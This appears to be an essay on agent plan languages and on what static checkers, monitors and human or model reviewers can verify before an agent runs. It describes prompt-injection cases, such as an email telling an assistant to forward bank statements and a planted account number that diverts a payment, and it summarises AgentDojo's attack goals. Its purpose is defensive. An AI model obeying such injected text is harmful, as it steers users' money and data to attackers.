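# The tradeoff between expressiveness and checkability in agent plan languages

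## Plans, checkers and executors

An AI agent is a program in which a large language model works through a task by calling tools, which are operations such as reading mail, looking up a record or sending money. Some agents call tools one at a time as they go. In others, the model first writes a plan containing all the steps, a separate program checks it, and the tools run only if the plan passes. The plan language is the notation the model writes in, together with the rules for what each step means. Designers have used plain English, lists of tool calls, small languages with limited branches and loops, and full programming languages with types. A richer language lets the agent take on more tasks, but the checking program can usually establish less about a plan before it runs.

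The language model that writes the plan is the proposer. The checker is the program or person that accepts or rejects the plan, and the executor is the program or model that carries out an accepted one. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent that keeps these roles strictly separate. Its proposer runs once per request and writes a complete plan before any tool runs. The checker compares the plan with a security policy, and a simple interpreter then executes the accepted steps and cannot add, remove or reorder any. If the checker rejects the plan, the request fails. The proposer receives no explanation and no second try, so it cannot keep adjusting an unsafe plan until the checker accepts it.

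An executor that is itself a language model may deviate from the plan it receives. *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?* (2026) treats this failure as separate from choosing a bad plan. A checker's approval is therefore useful only to the extent that the executor follows the approved plan.

### Agents without a whole plan

Many agents give a checker no complete plan to look at. Yao, Zhao and colleagues (2022), in *ReAct*, set out the best-known pattern, a loop of thought, action and observation. At step $t$ the model has in front of it the context

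$$c_t = (o_1, a_1, \dots, o_{t-1}, a_{t-1}, o_t),$$

which holds every observation $o$ and every action $a$ so far, and it picks the next action $a_t$ on that basis. Some of its "actions" are thoughts: pieces of text that change nothing in the outside world but join the context and steer later choices.

The loop handles unexpected results well. If a search returns nothing, the model can try another, even if nobody foresaw the failure. Yao and colleagues found that the loop beat agents trained by imitation or reinforcement learning by 34 percentage points on ALFWorld, a text game about household chores, and by 10 points on WebShop, a simulated online store.

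An overseer can inspect each action as it comes up but can't inspect the whole run until it ends, because each action depends on an observation that has yet to arrive. Action $a_7$, for example, does not exist until observation $o_7$ has arrived. An early thought may contain something that looks like a plan, but nothing ties the later actions to it.

### The invoice task

Suppose a user gives an agent this instruction: "Find the unpaid invoices in my inbox, pay each one from an approved supplier if it is under $500, and tell me the total paid." It is an ordinary office chore, and already awkward to plan in full, since nobody knows how many invoices there are or what they cost until the agent has read the mail. Before letting the agent near a bank account, an overseer might want to know five things:

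- That the plan ends. An agent that searches the inbox again after every payment could run forever if it mistakes the payment receipts for new invoices.
- Which tools it can use. The job calls for reading mail, looking up suppliers and sending payments. It gives no reason to delete mail or edit the supplier list.
- In what order it uses them. For each invoice, the supplier lookup and the comparison with $500 have to come before the payment.
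- Where data flows. An amount and an account number travel from an email to the payment tool, and the contents of the inbox should not travel to a stranger.
- Whether the result is right. The agent should pay every qualifying invoice once, pay no others, and report the correct sum.

Checking which tools a plan calls is easier than checking whether its result is right. In a language where every tool call appears by name, a checker can find the tools by reading the plan from top to bottom. To check the result, it needs a formal statement of what "right" means, and language models have been poor at writing these. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviews 38 studies on specifying and checking agent plans. It cites one benchmark on which models translated English into PDDL, a standard notation for planning problems, with the correct meaning only 24.8% to 34.2% of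 the time. If the translation is wrong, a checker can give a valid proof that a plan meets the formal statement even though the plan does something the user never asked for.

### Static checks, runtime checks and false rejections

A static check examines the text of the plan before any step runs. A runtime check happens during execution, when the actual values are available. *Soteria* (2026) applies both to one rule in a flight reservation agent, which must call a tool named No-Flown before any call to the tool that cancels a booking. The static checker rejected one plan because no route to the cancellation contained the No-Flown call. During execution, a monitor records the calls made. If the executor tries to cancel without the earlier call, the monitor blocks the attempt and prompts the executor to call No-Flown first.

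The static check covers every route through the plan before the agent acts, including routes that the current data would never trigger. But it cannot detect that the third invoice is for $612. The runtime check can, though by then the agent may have paid the first two, and stopping would leave the job half done.

Blocking an unsafe action also does not make an agent behave well afterwards. In their survey, Dantas and colleagues describe a study of agents that carry out transactions for customers, in which a runtime guard stopped 94% of unsafe actions. In most settings the agents still completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. The survey notes that this single study has not yet been replicated, but the mechanism is plausible because a guard that judges one action at a time does not check where the sequence is heading.

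A checker is sound if it never accepts a plan that breaks the stated policy. Even a checker that rejects every plan is sound, so false rejections also matter. A false rejection occurs when a checker rejects a plan that would have obeyed the policy. For example, a plan might compare each invoice with $500 early on, store the answer as a yes or no, and pay later if the answer was yes. This plan obeys the policy, but a checker that looks only for a comparison directly before each payment will reject it.

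Better engineering can reduce such cases but cannot always remove them. For most questions about what a program in a full programming language does, computability theory rules out a checker that is sound, always finishes and never rejects falsely. Dantas and colleagues found no approach that was sound, complete (roughly, free of false rejections), scalable, faithful to the meaning of the task and useful all at once.

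### Earlier cases of limiting a language

Computer scientists faced this problem long before language models. In the 1990s, web browsers began to download and run small Java programs, called applets, written by strangers. Java programs are distributed as bytecode, a compact set of simple instructions, which is verified before it runs. The verifier checks, among other things, that each instruction receives data of the right type and that every jump leads to a valid instruction. Java's designers chose the instruction set so that the verifier could check these properties quickly without running the program.

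Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn (2006) turned the idea into advice for the World Wide Web Consortium, which sets web standards. *The Rule of Least Power* recommends choosing the least powerful language suitable for the purpose. Its example is weather data. If the data is published as a plain table, any program can average it or combine it with other data. If the same data is inside an applet, a search engine can't extract it or even detect that the applet is about the weather, because finding out what an applet does generally requires running it.

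An applet can pass bytecode verification and still be the textbook case of an opaque program. The verifier checks its types and jumps, but a search engine cannot determine what the applet means. A language is checkable with respect to some property, so calling it "checkable" is incomplete without naming that property.

The rule is a limited precedent for agent plans. On a W3C mailing list, Mendelsohn later agreed with a correspondent that it concerned the reuse of information published on the Web and was never meant as a general design principle. The finding also warns against choosing a language that is too weak, because people then write workarounds that are themselves hard to follow. The underlying reasoning, that more powerful languages are harder to analyze, does apply to agent plans. Whether the least powerful language is the best choice for an agent depends on what the agent fails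 to do when limited to it.

### Three senses of expressiveness

Expressiveness is the range of behaviours that a proposer can write in a plan language. But people use the word in at least three senses, and they often mistake an argument about one for an argument about another.

In one sense, a language's expressiveness is what a proposer can write in it at all. A fixed list of payments, with no loops or branches, cannot express "pay each invoice under $500" for an inbox nobody has read yet. Turing-complete languages, at the other extreme, can compute anything that any computer can. Haskell and C are equally expressive in this sense, but Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn observe that programs in functional languages such as Haskell may be easier to analyse. Equally expressive languages can therefore differ in how much a checker can learn about a program.

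Another benefit of expressiveness is brevity. If the user is sure that the inbox never holds more than fifty invoices, a language with branches but no loops is enough, because the proposer can write out the conditional payment fifty times. This plan behaves the same as a three-line loop, but it is much longer, and a human checker is more likely to miss a mistake in one of the copies.

Which tasks a model completes in a given plan language depends on the model's skill with the notation and on the machinery that runs the plan, as well as on the notation itself. In *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?*, the proposer picks one of four styles of planning and a fixed router sends the task to an executor built for that style. On ALFWorld, agents that wrote a plan and then worked through it in a ReAct loop had a success rate of 48%, compared with 92% for the specialised executors. On SWE-bench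 Verified, a set of real software bugs, the figures were 36% and 44%. Benchmark scores measure expressiveness only in the practical sense of which tasks a model completes. A low score for a restricted language may mean that the language cannot express the tasks or that the model writes it badly.

### Mistakes, prompt injection and AgentDojo

An overseer has reason to care about this even when nobody is attacking. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes cases in which the company's model Claude submitted a sensitive form on a real website when it should not have, and worked around a restriction to reach data that required a token or a fee. Anthropic judged the real-world impact minimal.

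Attackers make matters worse, mainly through prompt injection, in which text in the data an agent reads gets the model to follow someone else's instructions. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) traces the weakness to language models operating directly on text, with no formal way to tell instructions from data. An email in the user's inbox might contain an invoice and a line telling the assistant to forward all bank statements to some address. In a ReAct loop, that line enters the context from which the model picks its next action.

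If the proposer writes the whole plan before anyone opens the mail, an instruction hidden in the mail can't change the steps, but an attacker can still divert the money. Girrens and Wang give the example of an agent that fetches an invoice on Monday and stores its details, including an account number that an attacker has planted. On Tuesday the user asks the agent to pay the invoice. The agent follows exactly the steps the user wanted, but the false account number sends the payment to the attacker, with no need for a hidden instruction.

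Researchers commonly test defences against such attacks on AgentDojo, a benchmark by Debenedetti and colleagues. It simulates four working environments, each with its own tools, user tasks and injection tasks (the attacker's goals). The security cases are every possible pairing of a user task with an injection task from the same environment.

| Environment | User tasks | Injection tasks | Security cases |
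|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (mail, calendar, files) | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack (team messages, web pages) | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel (flights, hotels, cars) | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking (transfers, statements) | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 |

In one banking task, the agent must pay a bill stored in a text file, and one of the attacker's goals in that environment is to send as much money as possible to the attacker's account. Task success is the share of user tasks the agent solves when there is no attack. Attack success is the share of security cases in which the attacker achieves the goal. A third measure counts the security cases in which the agent still completes the user's task without harmful side effects. Ordinary code determines each outcome by checking the state of the simulated environment afterwards, for instance whether a transfer took place. The designers avoided using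 a language model as judge because an injection that fooled the agent might fool the judge too.

The benchmark has grown since 2024, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports over 900 combinations, so percentages from different years do not always refer to the same cases. Attack success should also be read alongside task success, since an agent that refuses all work has an attack success rate of zero. A measured rate of zero covers only the attacks that the testers tried, whereas a sound checker guarantees that every plan it accepts complies with its policy.

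Girrens and Wang report that with their plan-first agent's data-flow checks switched on, attack success on AgentDojo was 0% under one standard attack. Task success without any attack fell from 53.0% to 29.0%, mainly because the checker rejected plans that passed untrusted data into sensitive actions. These rejections were correct under the policy, but the policy rules out tasks such as paying an invoice, which requires passing an amount and an account number from someone else's email into a payment.

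## What can be decided before a plan runs

How much a checker can establish about a plan depends on the constructs the proposer may use. An overseer of the invoice task may ask whether the plan ends, which tools it uses, in what order it uses them, where data flows, and whether the result is right. Each construct added to the language makes some of these questions harder to answer, and a few become impossible to answer in general.

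### Sequences

Dantas and colleagues define a plan as a finite sequence of actions, $\pi = (a_1, \dots, a_n)$, which is the easiest kind to check. Suppose the user already knows of two unpaid invoices, for $120 and $340, and the plan looks up the first supplier, pays it, looks up the second, pays it and reports $460. The checker starts from a description of the bank balance, the supplier list and the unpaid invoices. For each action, it tests whether the policy allows that action in the current state, then updates the state with the action's effects.

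The checker can answer all five questions in one pass through the plan. The plan ends as long as every tool call returns. Its text lists the tools in the order it uses them, and the checker can follow each value from the step that produces it to the steps that use it. If someone has written a formal statement of what the user wants, the checker can compare the final state with it.

This works because the checker is given the starting state and the effects of each action. Otherwise it has to track every state the world might be in. Lang and Zanuttini (2013), in *Knowledge-Based Programs as Plans*, represent an agent's knowledge as such a set of states. With $m$ unknown yes-or-no facts, the set can hold up to $2^m$ states, and an action with an uncertain outcome, such as a transfer that may fail silently, can enlarge it. So even a plan with no branches can take a lot of computation to check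 in an uncertain world.

### Branches

A branch lets a plan respond to what it finds. Suppose the inbox holds exactly twenty invoices, and the proposer writes out twenty conditional payments: if this supplier is on the approved list and the amount is under $500, pay, otherwise skip. The plan still ends, because each step runs at most once, and its text still names every tool it could call. But each condition doubles the number of routes through the plan, so twenty of them give up to

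$$2^{20} = 1{,}048{,}576$$

paths. A checker that spends a millisecond on each needs about seventeen and a half minutes. For forty invoices it needs almost 35 years.

The usual remedy is for the checker to merge its results for the two arms of each branch into one summary and continue from that. For the twenty payments, it examines forty arms and merges twenty times, taking sixty steps instead of following a million paths. The check remains sound because the summary covers everything either arm could have done. But the summary also covers combinations that no run could produce, and these cause false rejections.

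Das, Lerner and Seigle (2002), in *ESP*, illustrate the problem with a simplified fragment of the GNU C compiler. The program opens a file if a certain flag is on, goes through an unrelated branch, and then closes the file if the flag is on. Every run obeys the rule that a program may close only a file it has opened. After the first branch, however, a merging checker records only that the file may or may not be open. It doesn't record that this depends on the flag, so it reports an error at the closing step.

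An invoice plan can have the same structure. It looks up the supplier if the amount is under $500, then files the due date in one of two calendars, then pays if the amount is under $500. The plan never pays without a lookup. But after merging the branches, the checker records only that the lookup may have happened, so it rejects the plan.

Das and colleagues avoid this error by merging more selectively. Their checker models the rule as a state machine, which for the invoice plan would have the states "not looked up", "looked up" and "violated". It merges two summaries only if the machine is in the same state in both. After the first branch it therefore keeps one summary for "looked up" with an amount under $500 and another for "not looked up" with an amount of $500 or more. The calendar branch splits these into four, but it does not change the machine's state, so the checker merges them back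 into two. Only the "looked up" summary can reach the payment, so the plan passes.

The running time is now polynomial: $O(V^2|E||D|)$ for $V$ variables, $|E|$ connections between steps and $|D|$ states in the machine. A single machine that tracked all twenty lookups would bring back the $2^{20}$ combinations, but the checker can instead make twenty passes and follow one invoice in each. Das and colleagues likewise made one pass for each of the fifteen files the compiler writes to. They proved that all 646 calls to one printing function write to valid, open files. The program has 140,000 lines, and each pass took about 70 seconds on average.

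The checker still rejects some plans that obey the rule. Suppose a plan first compares the amount with $500 and stores the answer as "small" or "not small". This branch does not affect the machine, so the checker merges its arms and loses the link between the stored answer and the amount. If the plan then looks up the supplier when the stored answer is "small", and pays when the amount is under $500, the checker rejects it even though it obeys the rule.

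A checker can also merge without losing information. *Efficient State Merging in Symbolic Execution* (Kuznetsov, Kinder and colleagues, 2012) gives the example of a program that sets $x$ to 0 if its input is negative and to 5 otherwise. The checker can record the value of $x$ as the formula "0 if the input is negative, else 5" rather than as "0 or 5". This avoids the false alarm, but the formulas grow with every merge, which makes more work for the solver, the program that must later decide whether they can be true together. The paper cites an earlier experiment in which merging at every opportunity increased the total solving time in two of three test programs. The paper's own method merges only where it estimates that merging will save work, and it was several orders of magnitude faster than previously published results on 96 standard command-line programs.

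### Loops over a finite collection

Written-out conditionals don't work if the number of invoices is unknown when the plan is written. Girrens and Wang's plan language has a loop that runs its body once for each element of a collection. The executor fixes the collection before the loop starts, so payment receipts that arrive in the inbox while it runs do not lengthen it. The loop therefore ends if every tool call in its body ends, which a time limit on each call can ensure. Nesting multiplies the work but keeps it predictable, since $d$ nested loops over lists of at most $m$ items run the innermost body at most $m^d$ times.

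Checking is also easier because this language has no arithmetic and discards any variable created inside a branch or loop body when that block ends. After a branch, the checker has no new variables to reconcile between the two arms. One pass through a loop body covers every iteration, because no variable carries a value from one iteration to the next. If the checker allows for any tool output, a payment inside the loop is possible exactly when some element could satisfy the finite list of comparisons that guard it. Questions about tools, order and data flow are then no harder to answer than they are for branches.

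The drawback is that the loop cannot handle the last part of the user's request, "tell me the total paid", because it can neither add the amounts nor pass a running total to the next step. The plan could pass all the invoices to a quarantined model, a language model that reads untrusted text but cannot call tools, to compute the sum. But nothing would guarantee that the model's answer matched the payments that went through.

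Tools can also restore abilities that the language leaves out. For example, a loop with access to a calculator and a notepad can keep a running total by reading a number from the notepad, adding an amount and writing the result back. A checker that allows for any tool output remains sound, but it cannot determine anything about the total.

### Loops that carry numbers

In *The complexity of loop programs* (1967), Meyer and Ritchie studied LOOP, a language in which every program ends but loops can do arithmetic. LOOP programs work on non-negative whole numbers held in registers. An instruction can copy one register into another, add one to a register, or set it to zero. LOOP X … END repeats the enclosed instructions as many times as the number in X when the loop starts. Changing X inside the loop does not change the number of repetitions, so a program with only "X = X + 1" inside LOOP X doubles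 X and stops.

LOOP programs compute exactly the primitive recursive functions, a large class that includes nearly all the arithmetic anyone uses. They can add, multiply, compute powers and find the $x$-th prime number. Meyer and Ritchie show how to subtract in LOOP, with zero in place of any negative result. The invoice plan can therefore test whether an amount is under $500 by subtracting it in cents from 50,000 and checking whether the result is positive.

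Every LOOP program ends, but it may take an absurdly long time. Consider this one, started with 50 in X and 1 in Y:

```
LOOP X
  LOOP Y
    Y = Y + 1
  END
END
```

Each pass of the outer loop doubles Y. After fifty passes Y is $2^{50}$, about $1.1 \times 10^{15}$, and a machine that performs a billion additions a second takes thirteen days to reach it. By comparison, two nested loops over a list of fifty invoices run their body 2,500 times.

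Meyer and Ritchie prove an upper limit on a program's running time that a checker can compute from the program's text. They define a series of functions in which $f_1(x) = 2x$ for positive $x$, $f_2(x) = 2^x$, and $f_3(x)$ is a tower of $x$ twos, each the exponent of the one below. If a program has $k$ instructions and nests its loops $n$ deep, its running time is at most $f_n$ applied $k$ times to the largest input. This limit is already useless for loops nested three deep, since $f_3(5)$ has 19,729 digits. They remark that a program that actually needs time $f_7$ would run beyond the lifetime of the Milky Way on any input larger than two. A checker could set a lower limit for programs that run faster than their nesting suggests, but Meyer and Ritchie prove that no algorithm can always identify these programs when loops are nested three deep or more.

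Even when every plan is guaranteed to terminate, a checker may be unable to decide whether two plans are equivalent, meaning that they give the same output for every input. An equivalence test would let the checker compare a proposed plan with a trusted one, but *The Equivalence Problem of Simple Programs* (1970) proves that no algorithm can decide equivalence for all LOOP programs with loops nested two deep.

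No algorithm can decide whether two LOOP programs are equivalent. For any program $M$ in a full programming language, we can write a LOOP program that receives a number $t$, simulates $M$ for $t$ steps, and outputs 1 if $M$ has stopped by then and 0 otherwise. A bounded loop is enough, since it only has to repeat a single-step simulation $t$ times. This program is equivalent to one that always outputs 0 exactly when $M$ never stops. An algorithm for equivalence would therefore solve the halting problem, which no algorithm can do.

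The same construction shows that a checker cannot always determine whether a plan could delete a user's mail. Suppose a plan simulates a program for up to $t$ steps, where $t$ is the number of messages in the inbox, and deletes all mail if the program stops within those steps. This plan always ends, and the deletion tool appears in its text. But whether any inbox size would trigger the deletion is undecidable, meaning that no algorithm can answer correctly for every simulated program. A checker can therefore list the tools that appear in a LOOP program, but it cannot always determine which of them could run, in what order, or on what data.

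The difficulty comes from covering all inputs at once. If the inbox holds at most fifty messages, the checker can simulate the plan for each size from 0 to 50, given enough time. The difficulty also depends on whether loops are nested. *On the Computational Complexity of Program Scheme Equivalence* (Hunt, Constable and Sahni, 1980) classifies equivalence as NP-complete for LOOP programs without nesting. An algorithm exists for this problem, but no known algorithm is fast in every case.

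### Unbounded loops and Rice's theorem

Some tasks need a loop with no preset limit, such as "check every minute until the bank confirms the transfer". *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) uses a plan language that permits such loops. A plan is a finite list of numbered commands, and a jump can move execution to any of them. A backward jump repeats part of the plan, possibly forever, so a checker can no longer assume that the plan will end. If plans can store numbers of any size, deciding whether a plan ends is the halting problem.

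No program can always tell whether a given program stops on a given input. To prove this, suppose a program $H$ could. We could then write a program $q$ that takes the text of any program $p$ and uses $H$ to check whether $p$ stops when given its own text. If $H$ outputs yes, $q$ runs forever, and if $H$ outputs no, $q$ stops. When $q$ is given its own text, either output from $H$ is wrong, so $H$ cannot exist.

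Rice (1953), in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, extended the result from halting to nearly every question about what programs do. Let $\varphi_e$ be the function that program $e$ computes, undefined on any input for which $e$ never stops. Let $C$ be a nonempty set of computable functions that omits at least one computable function. Then no algorithm can decide, for every program $e$, whether $\varphi_e$ belongs to $C$. Rice proved this for the sets of numbers that programs generate, but the version for functions is now the usual one.

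The proof turns any such algorithm into a solution of the halting problem:

1. Suppose an algorithm $A$ decides membership in $C$. Assume that the function which is undefined everywhere lies outside $C$. (If it lies inside, use the complement of $C$ instead.)
2. Pick a program $b$ whose function is in $C$.
3. To find out whether some program $a$ stops on an input $i$, write a new program $t$. Given any input $x$, it first runs $a$ on $i$, throws the result away, and then runs $b$ on $x$.
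4. If $a$ stops on $i$, then $t$ computes the same function as $b$, which is in $C$. If $a$ does not stop, $t$ never gets past its first stage, so its function is undefined everywhere and lies outside $C$.
5. Running $A$ on the text of $t$ therefore reveals whether $a$ stops on $i$, which no algorithm can do in general.

The same argument works for tool calls. If a plan first runs $a$ on $i$ without using any tools, and then deletes the user's mail, the mail will be deleted if and only if $a$ stops.

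The theorem concerns what a program computes, so it does not apply to questions about the text, such as whether the word "delete" occurs in a plan. It also does not apply to questions with a time limit. *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider) gives "terminates within 100 computational steps" as an example of a policy that a static check can enforce exactly, and "eventually terminates" as one that it cannot. A program can read at most 100 symbols of input in 100 steps, so the checker can try every possible input of that length. Even with only two symbols there are $2^{100}$ such inputs, about $10^{30}$, so a decidable question can still be infeasible to answer.

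Rice also noted that special methods will exist for particular functions. The theorem rules out a single method that works for all programs, but an agent's plans are a small and fairly regular subset of them. Meyer and Ritchie similarly note that no algorithm can find every possible improvement to a program, yet compilers routinely improve large classes of common programs.

The theorem also does not apply if a plan and its world have only finitely many states between them. Suppose there are $N$ possible combinations of stored values and position in the plan, and each combination determines the next. A run of more than $N$ steps must repeat a combination, and will then repeat forever. A checker can therefore detect an endless loop by counting steps until the run exceeds $N$.

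Lang and Zanuttini study plans that branch on what the agent knows, so each position in the plan is paired with a set of possible states. The number of these pairs can be enormous. They cite a plan whose size grows only polynomially with a number $n$, but whose single run ends after $2^{2^n} - 1$ steps, or about $1.8 \times 10^{19}$ for $n = 6$. Checking such plans is EXPSPACE-hard, so in the worst case it needs memory exponential in the size of the problem.

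### Code written later

A plan may also contain a step whose content does not exist yet, such as "ask the model for a script and run it". Rice's theorem describes the limits on a checker that has the whole program. Here the checker has no code to analyse, so it can rely only on the restrictions that the executor will place on the code once it is generated. If the executor lets the code read mail but do nothing else, the code cannot pay anyone. If the executor also stops the code after a minute, the step is sure to end. The checker can establish nothing about the order of calls, the flow of data or the result within those restrictions.

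### Ways out

One response is to restrict the language until the questions become decidable, as Girrens and Wang do by leaving out arithmetic. The restriction can rule out some tasks and make the plans for others longer. Lang and Zanuttini prove that some planning problems have short solutions with unbounded loops but no comparably short ones without them, even though the world is finite.

A checker can instead accept a rich language and over-approximate, rejecting every plan it cannot clear. Hamlen and colleagues give the example of enforcing "eventually terminates" by accepting only programs that stop within 100 steps. Every accepted program terminates, but the checker also rejects one that would stop at step 101. Many program checkers similarly write a loop out a fixed number of times, say fifty, and test whether a fifty-first pass is possible. Without that test, the check would be unsound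 because it would miss a violation in the fifty-first pass.

A checker can have a high rejection rate without over-approximating badly. Girrens and Wang's data-flow check stopped about 53% of runs on AgentDojo and cut the share that reached execution from about 81% to about 37%. Most of the stopped runs had real policy violations, which a more precise checker would also have caught.

A checker can also require the proposer to supply a proof with the plan. Checking the steps of a written proof is mechanical, even when finding the proof is not. To show that a loop ends, the proposer could name a quantity that falls with every pass and cannot fall below zero, such as the number of invoices still to process. To show that the total is right, it needs a loop invariant, a statement that holds before the loop and after each pass, such as "the total equals the sum of the payments made so far".

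*Inadequacy of Computable Loop Invariants* describes a program with one loop and three variables, whose only arithmetic is adding one, doubling and halving. The program never stops if all three variables start at zero, but any invariant that would prove this is undecidable, meaning that no algorithm can always tell whether given values of the variables satisfy it. A checker that tests invariants by evaluating them therefore couldn't prove that the program runs forever. Loops in ordinary office tasks are unlikely to have this problem, and for them the harder part is getting a language model to write a correct invariant.

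The remaining option is to check the plan while it runs. A monitor can wait until a plan is about to delete mail and then block the call, so it doesn't have to predict whether the plan will ever do so. Hamlen and colleagues prove that monitors can in this way enforce policies that no static check can decide. If the block comes late, though, the system may have to undo earlier steps. A monitor can enforce a deadline, but it cannot enforce "the plan eventually ends", because there is no point at which a running plan has definitely broken that rule.

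A checker can also rewrite the plan before it runs, for instance by inserting the supplier lookup and the $500 comparison directly before every payment. The inserted tests stop payments that violate the policy, and a plan that already obeyed it still pays the same invoices. Rewriting can also enforce some policies that a monitor cannot. Hamlen and colleagues give the example of a secret file whose existence must not affect what a program does. A monitor would have to compare the actual run with one in which the file was absent, but a rewriter only has to remove the file's name from every directory listing the program receives.

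### Constructs and properties compared

The table below shows what a static check can establish for each construct, assuming that every tool call returns, that the checker has a description of what the tools do, and that someone has formally specified what counts as a correct result. No algorithm can answer the questions marked "Approximate" in every case, so a sound checker must sometimes reject a plan that obeys the policy.

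| Construct | Does it end? | Which tools? | In what order? | Where does data flow? | Is the result right? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sequence | Yes | Exact, from the text | Exact, in one pass | Exact, in one pass | Exact if the starting state is known |
| Branch | Yes | Exact list; which ones can run depends on the path | Exact over up to $2^n$ paths, or fast with false rejections | Same as for order | Exact over up to $2^n$ paths, for simple conditions |
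| Bounded loop without arithmetic or carried values | Yes, after a predictable number of passes | Same as for branches | Same as for branches, within one pass of the body | Same as for branches | Possible for each item; the loop cannot compute a total |
| Bounded loop with arithmetic and carried values | Yes, but perhaps not in any useful time | Exact list; approximate for which ones can run | Approximate | Approximate | Undecidable in general; a proof can settle particular plans |
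| Unbounded loop | Undecidable in general; decidable with finitely many states | Exact list; approximate for which ones can run | Approximate | Approximate | Undecidable in general; a proof can settle particular plans |
| Code written later | Only if the executor sets a time limit | Only the set that the executor allows | Unknown | Unknown, within the executor's limits | Unknown |

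## Plans written in free text

A proposer needs no special notation to write a plan. For the invoice task it might produce this:

1. Find the unpaid invoices in the inbox.
2. Check which of them come from approved suppliers and are under $500.
3. Pay those invoices.
4. Tell the user the total paid.

The plan covers the whole request and anyone can read it, but it leaves a lot open. The user may have a personal inbox and a shared one for accounts. "Approved" could refer to the finance department's list or to any supplier the company has paid before. If a payment times out, the executor has to decide whether to retry, which might pay the invoice twice.

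A static checker can establish very little from this text. It names no tools, so the checker cannot even determine which tools the plan uses. The agent could carry out step 2 with a database lookup, a web search or a guess based on the letterhead.

But the vagueness also helps the executor handle cases that nobody foresaw. An invoice may come from "Acme Ltd" when the approved list has "Acme Limited", arrive as a photograph, or turn out to be a reminder about a bill that the agent has just paid. A program would need a rule for each of these cases, whereas a language model can often work out what the user would want. *RunAgent* (Srivastava, Khojastepour et al., 2026) defends natural-language plans on this ground, arguing that rigid code cannot cope when exceptions arise or priorities shift.

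An executor that can fill gaps in a plan can also skip steps. *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?* measured how often a ReAct executor followed the written plan it was given. A rule-based program tested whether each run contained every step of the plan in order, ignoring extra actions in between. Depending on the model, 12% to 45% of runs passed on three of the four benchmarks, and 42% to 68% passed on the fourth, WebArena, a set of tasks on simulated websites. Runs with long plans passed much less often. With DeepSeek-V4 on Mind2Web, another web benchmark, the pass rate fell from 73% for the shortest plans to 6% for plans of more than ten steps. Some deviations may have been sensible, since an executor that skips an unnecessary step also fails this test.

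### Review by people

The obvious way to check a prose plan is to have the user read it. *Plan-Then-Execute* (He, Demartini and Gadiraju, 2025) tested this with 248 people and six everyday tasks, such as repaying a credit card and booking a flight, in a simulated environment. An agent built on GPT-3.5 wrote a numbered plan for each task; three plans were correct and three had flaws. Only some participants could edit the plan, and only some approved or corrected each action during execution.

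Participants then stated whether they trusted the plan to give a correct outcome. He et al. counted an answer as calibrated if the person trusted a correct plan or distrusted a flawed one. For correct plans, between 75% and 97% of answers were calibrated, depending on the task and the group. For flawed plans the figure was between 3% and 27%, because most people trusted those plans too.

The clearest case is a currency task with two transactions. Participants had learned in a tutorial that the executor could perform only one action per step, but the plan put both transactions into one step. The unedited plan failed every time, yet 80% to 89% of the people who saw it trusted it.

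The result of the credit-card task is not as bad as its score suggests. The plan had flaws, but the agent running unaided still got the right result for 78% of participants, presumably because the executor filled in what the plan lacked. Many people who trusted the plan were right about the outcome, but the study counted their trust as misplaced.

Letting people edit the plans did not make their trust better calibrated. It also lowered the average quality slightly, from 3.8 on a five-point scale to between 3.6 and 3.7, mainly because some participants damaged plans that were already correct. But editing raised the success rate of the currency plan from zero to between 10% and 13%.

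On one task, which involved a trip to Japan, people helped more during execution than during planning. The plan was correct, but the executor tended to pick an itinerary that did not match the request. When participants approved each action, success rose from at most 6% to over 20%. They may have found it easier to judge a particular itinerary than a plan step that said to choose one.

A better review screen might help people find more errors, but the evidence so far is weak. In *An Experimental Comparison of Cognitive Forcing Functions for Execution Plans*, Ghosh, Sarkar and colleagues (2026) had 214 people review plans and drafts for writing tasks. Three of the five plans contained a planted error: a wrong step, a missing step or a set of irrelevant steps. Before giving a verdict, some participants had to name an assumption behind the plan, and others had to consider what would happen if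 its most important step failed. Some did both, and a control group did neither.

People who named assumptions accepted the fewest faulty outputs, but the difference was statistically significant only against the what-if group, not the control group. In a second analysis that adjusted for differences between participants and tasks, the assumptions exercise was associated with less accurate feedback than the control. Participants found the what-if question more helpful.

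*Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026) reports a similar problem with records of what an agent has already done. Users missed small but consequential errors in the usual step-by-step display. A new interface that stated the task's requirements and the agent's assumptions made them faster and more confident, but didn't meaningfully change their accuracy.

### Review by a model

A language model can do the reading instead. *Plan Verification for LLM-Based Embodied Task Completion Agents* (2025) tested several models as judges of plans for household tasks. On a first reading, OpenAI's o4-mini found 80% of the defects, and 93% of its objections were correct. DeepSeek-R1 found 68% and raised no false objections. When the planning model revised its plan in response and the judge read it again, the share of defects found rose by 5% to 10% on average. Dantas and colleagues rate this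 study at high risk of bias, so the exact figures deserve little weight.

Judging results is not much more reliable. In *Why Do LLM-based Web Agents Fail?* (2026), a model judge's verdicts matched the researchers' on 41 of 50 checks of whether a step had achieved its purpose, and on 43 of 50 final evaluations.

*End-to-end PDDL Planning with Hardcoded and Dynamic Agents* (2025) argues that unless a model judge is demonstrably better than the model it judges, it may be unable to solve the problem itself and so fail to recognise a wrong solution. An injected instruction that ends up in the plan may also mislead the judge. A model judge can reduce the number of bad plans that reach the executor, but it is not a sound checker.

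### Translation into a formal model

A proof could provide the missing guarantee, but it requires a mathematical representation of the plan. *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods* (Ramani, Tawosi et al., 2025), a case study from JPMorgan, used a language model to translate prose plans into input for NuSMV. NuSMV is a model checker, a program that searches the possible runs of a system for one that breaks a given rule.

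The translation describes the plan as a Kripke structure. This consists of a finite set of states, the states in which a run may start, the permitted moves between states, and a list of the facts that hold in each state. For a single invoice, the translator would proceed roughly as follows:

1. It turns facts into yes-or-no variables, such as *checked* (the agent has checked the supplier) and *paid*.
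2. It sets their starting values, here "no" for both.
3. It writes each action as a change of state, with the conditions that must hold beforehand. The supplier check sets *checked* to "yes", and the payment sets *paid* to "yes".
4. It adds a variable that counts through the steps, so that the actions happen in the planned order.

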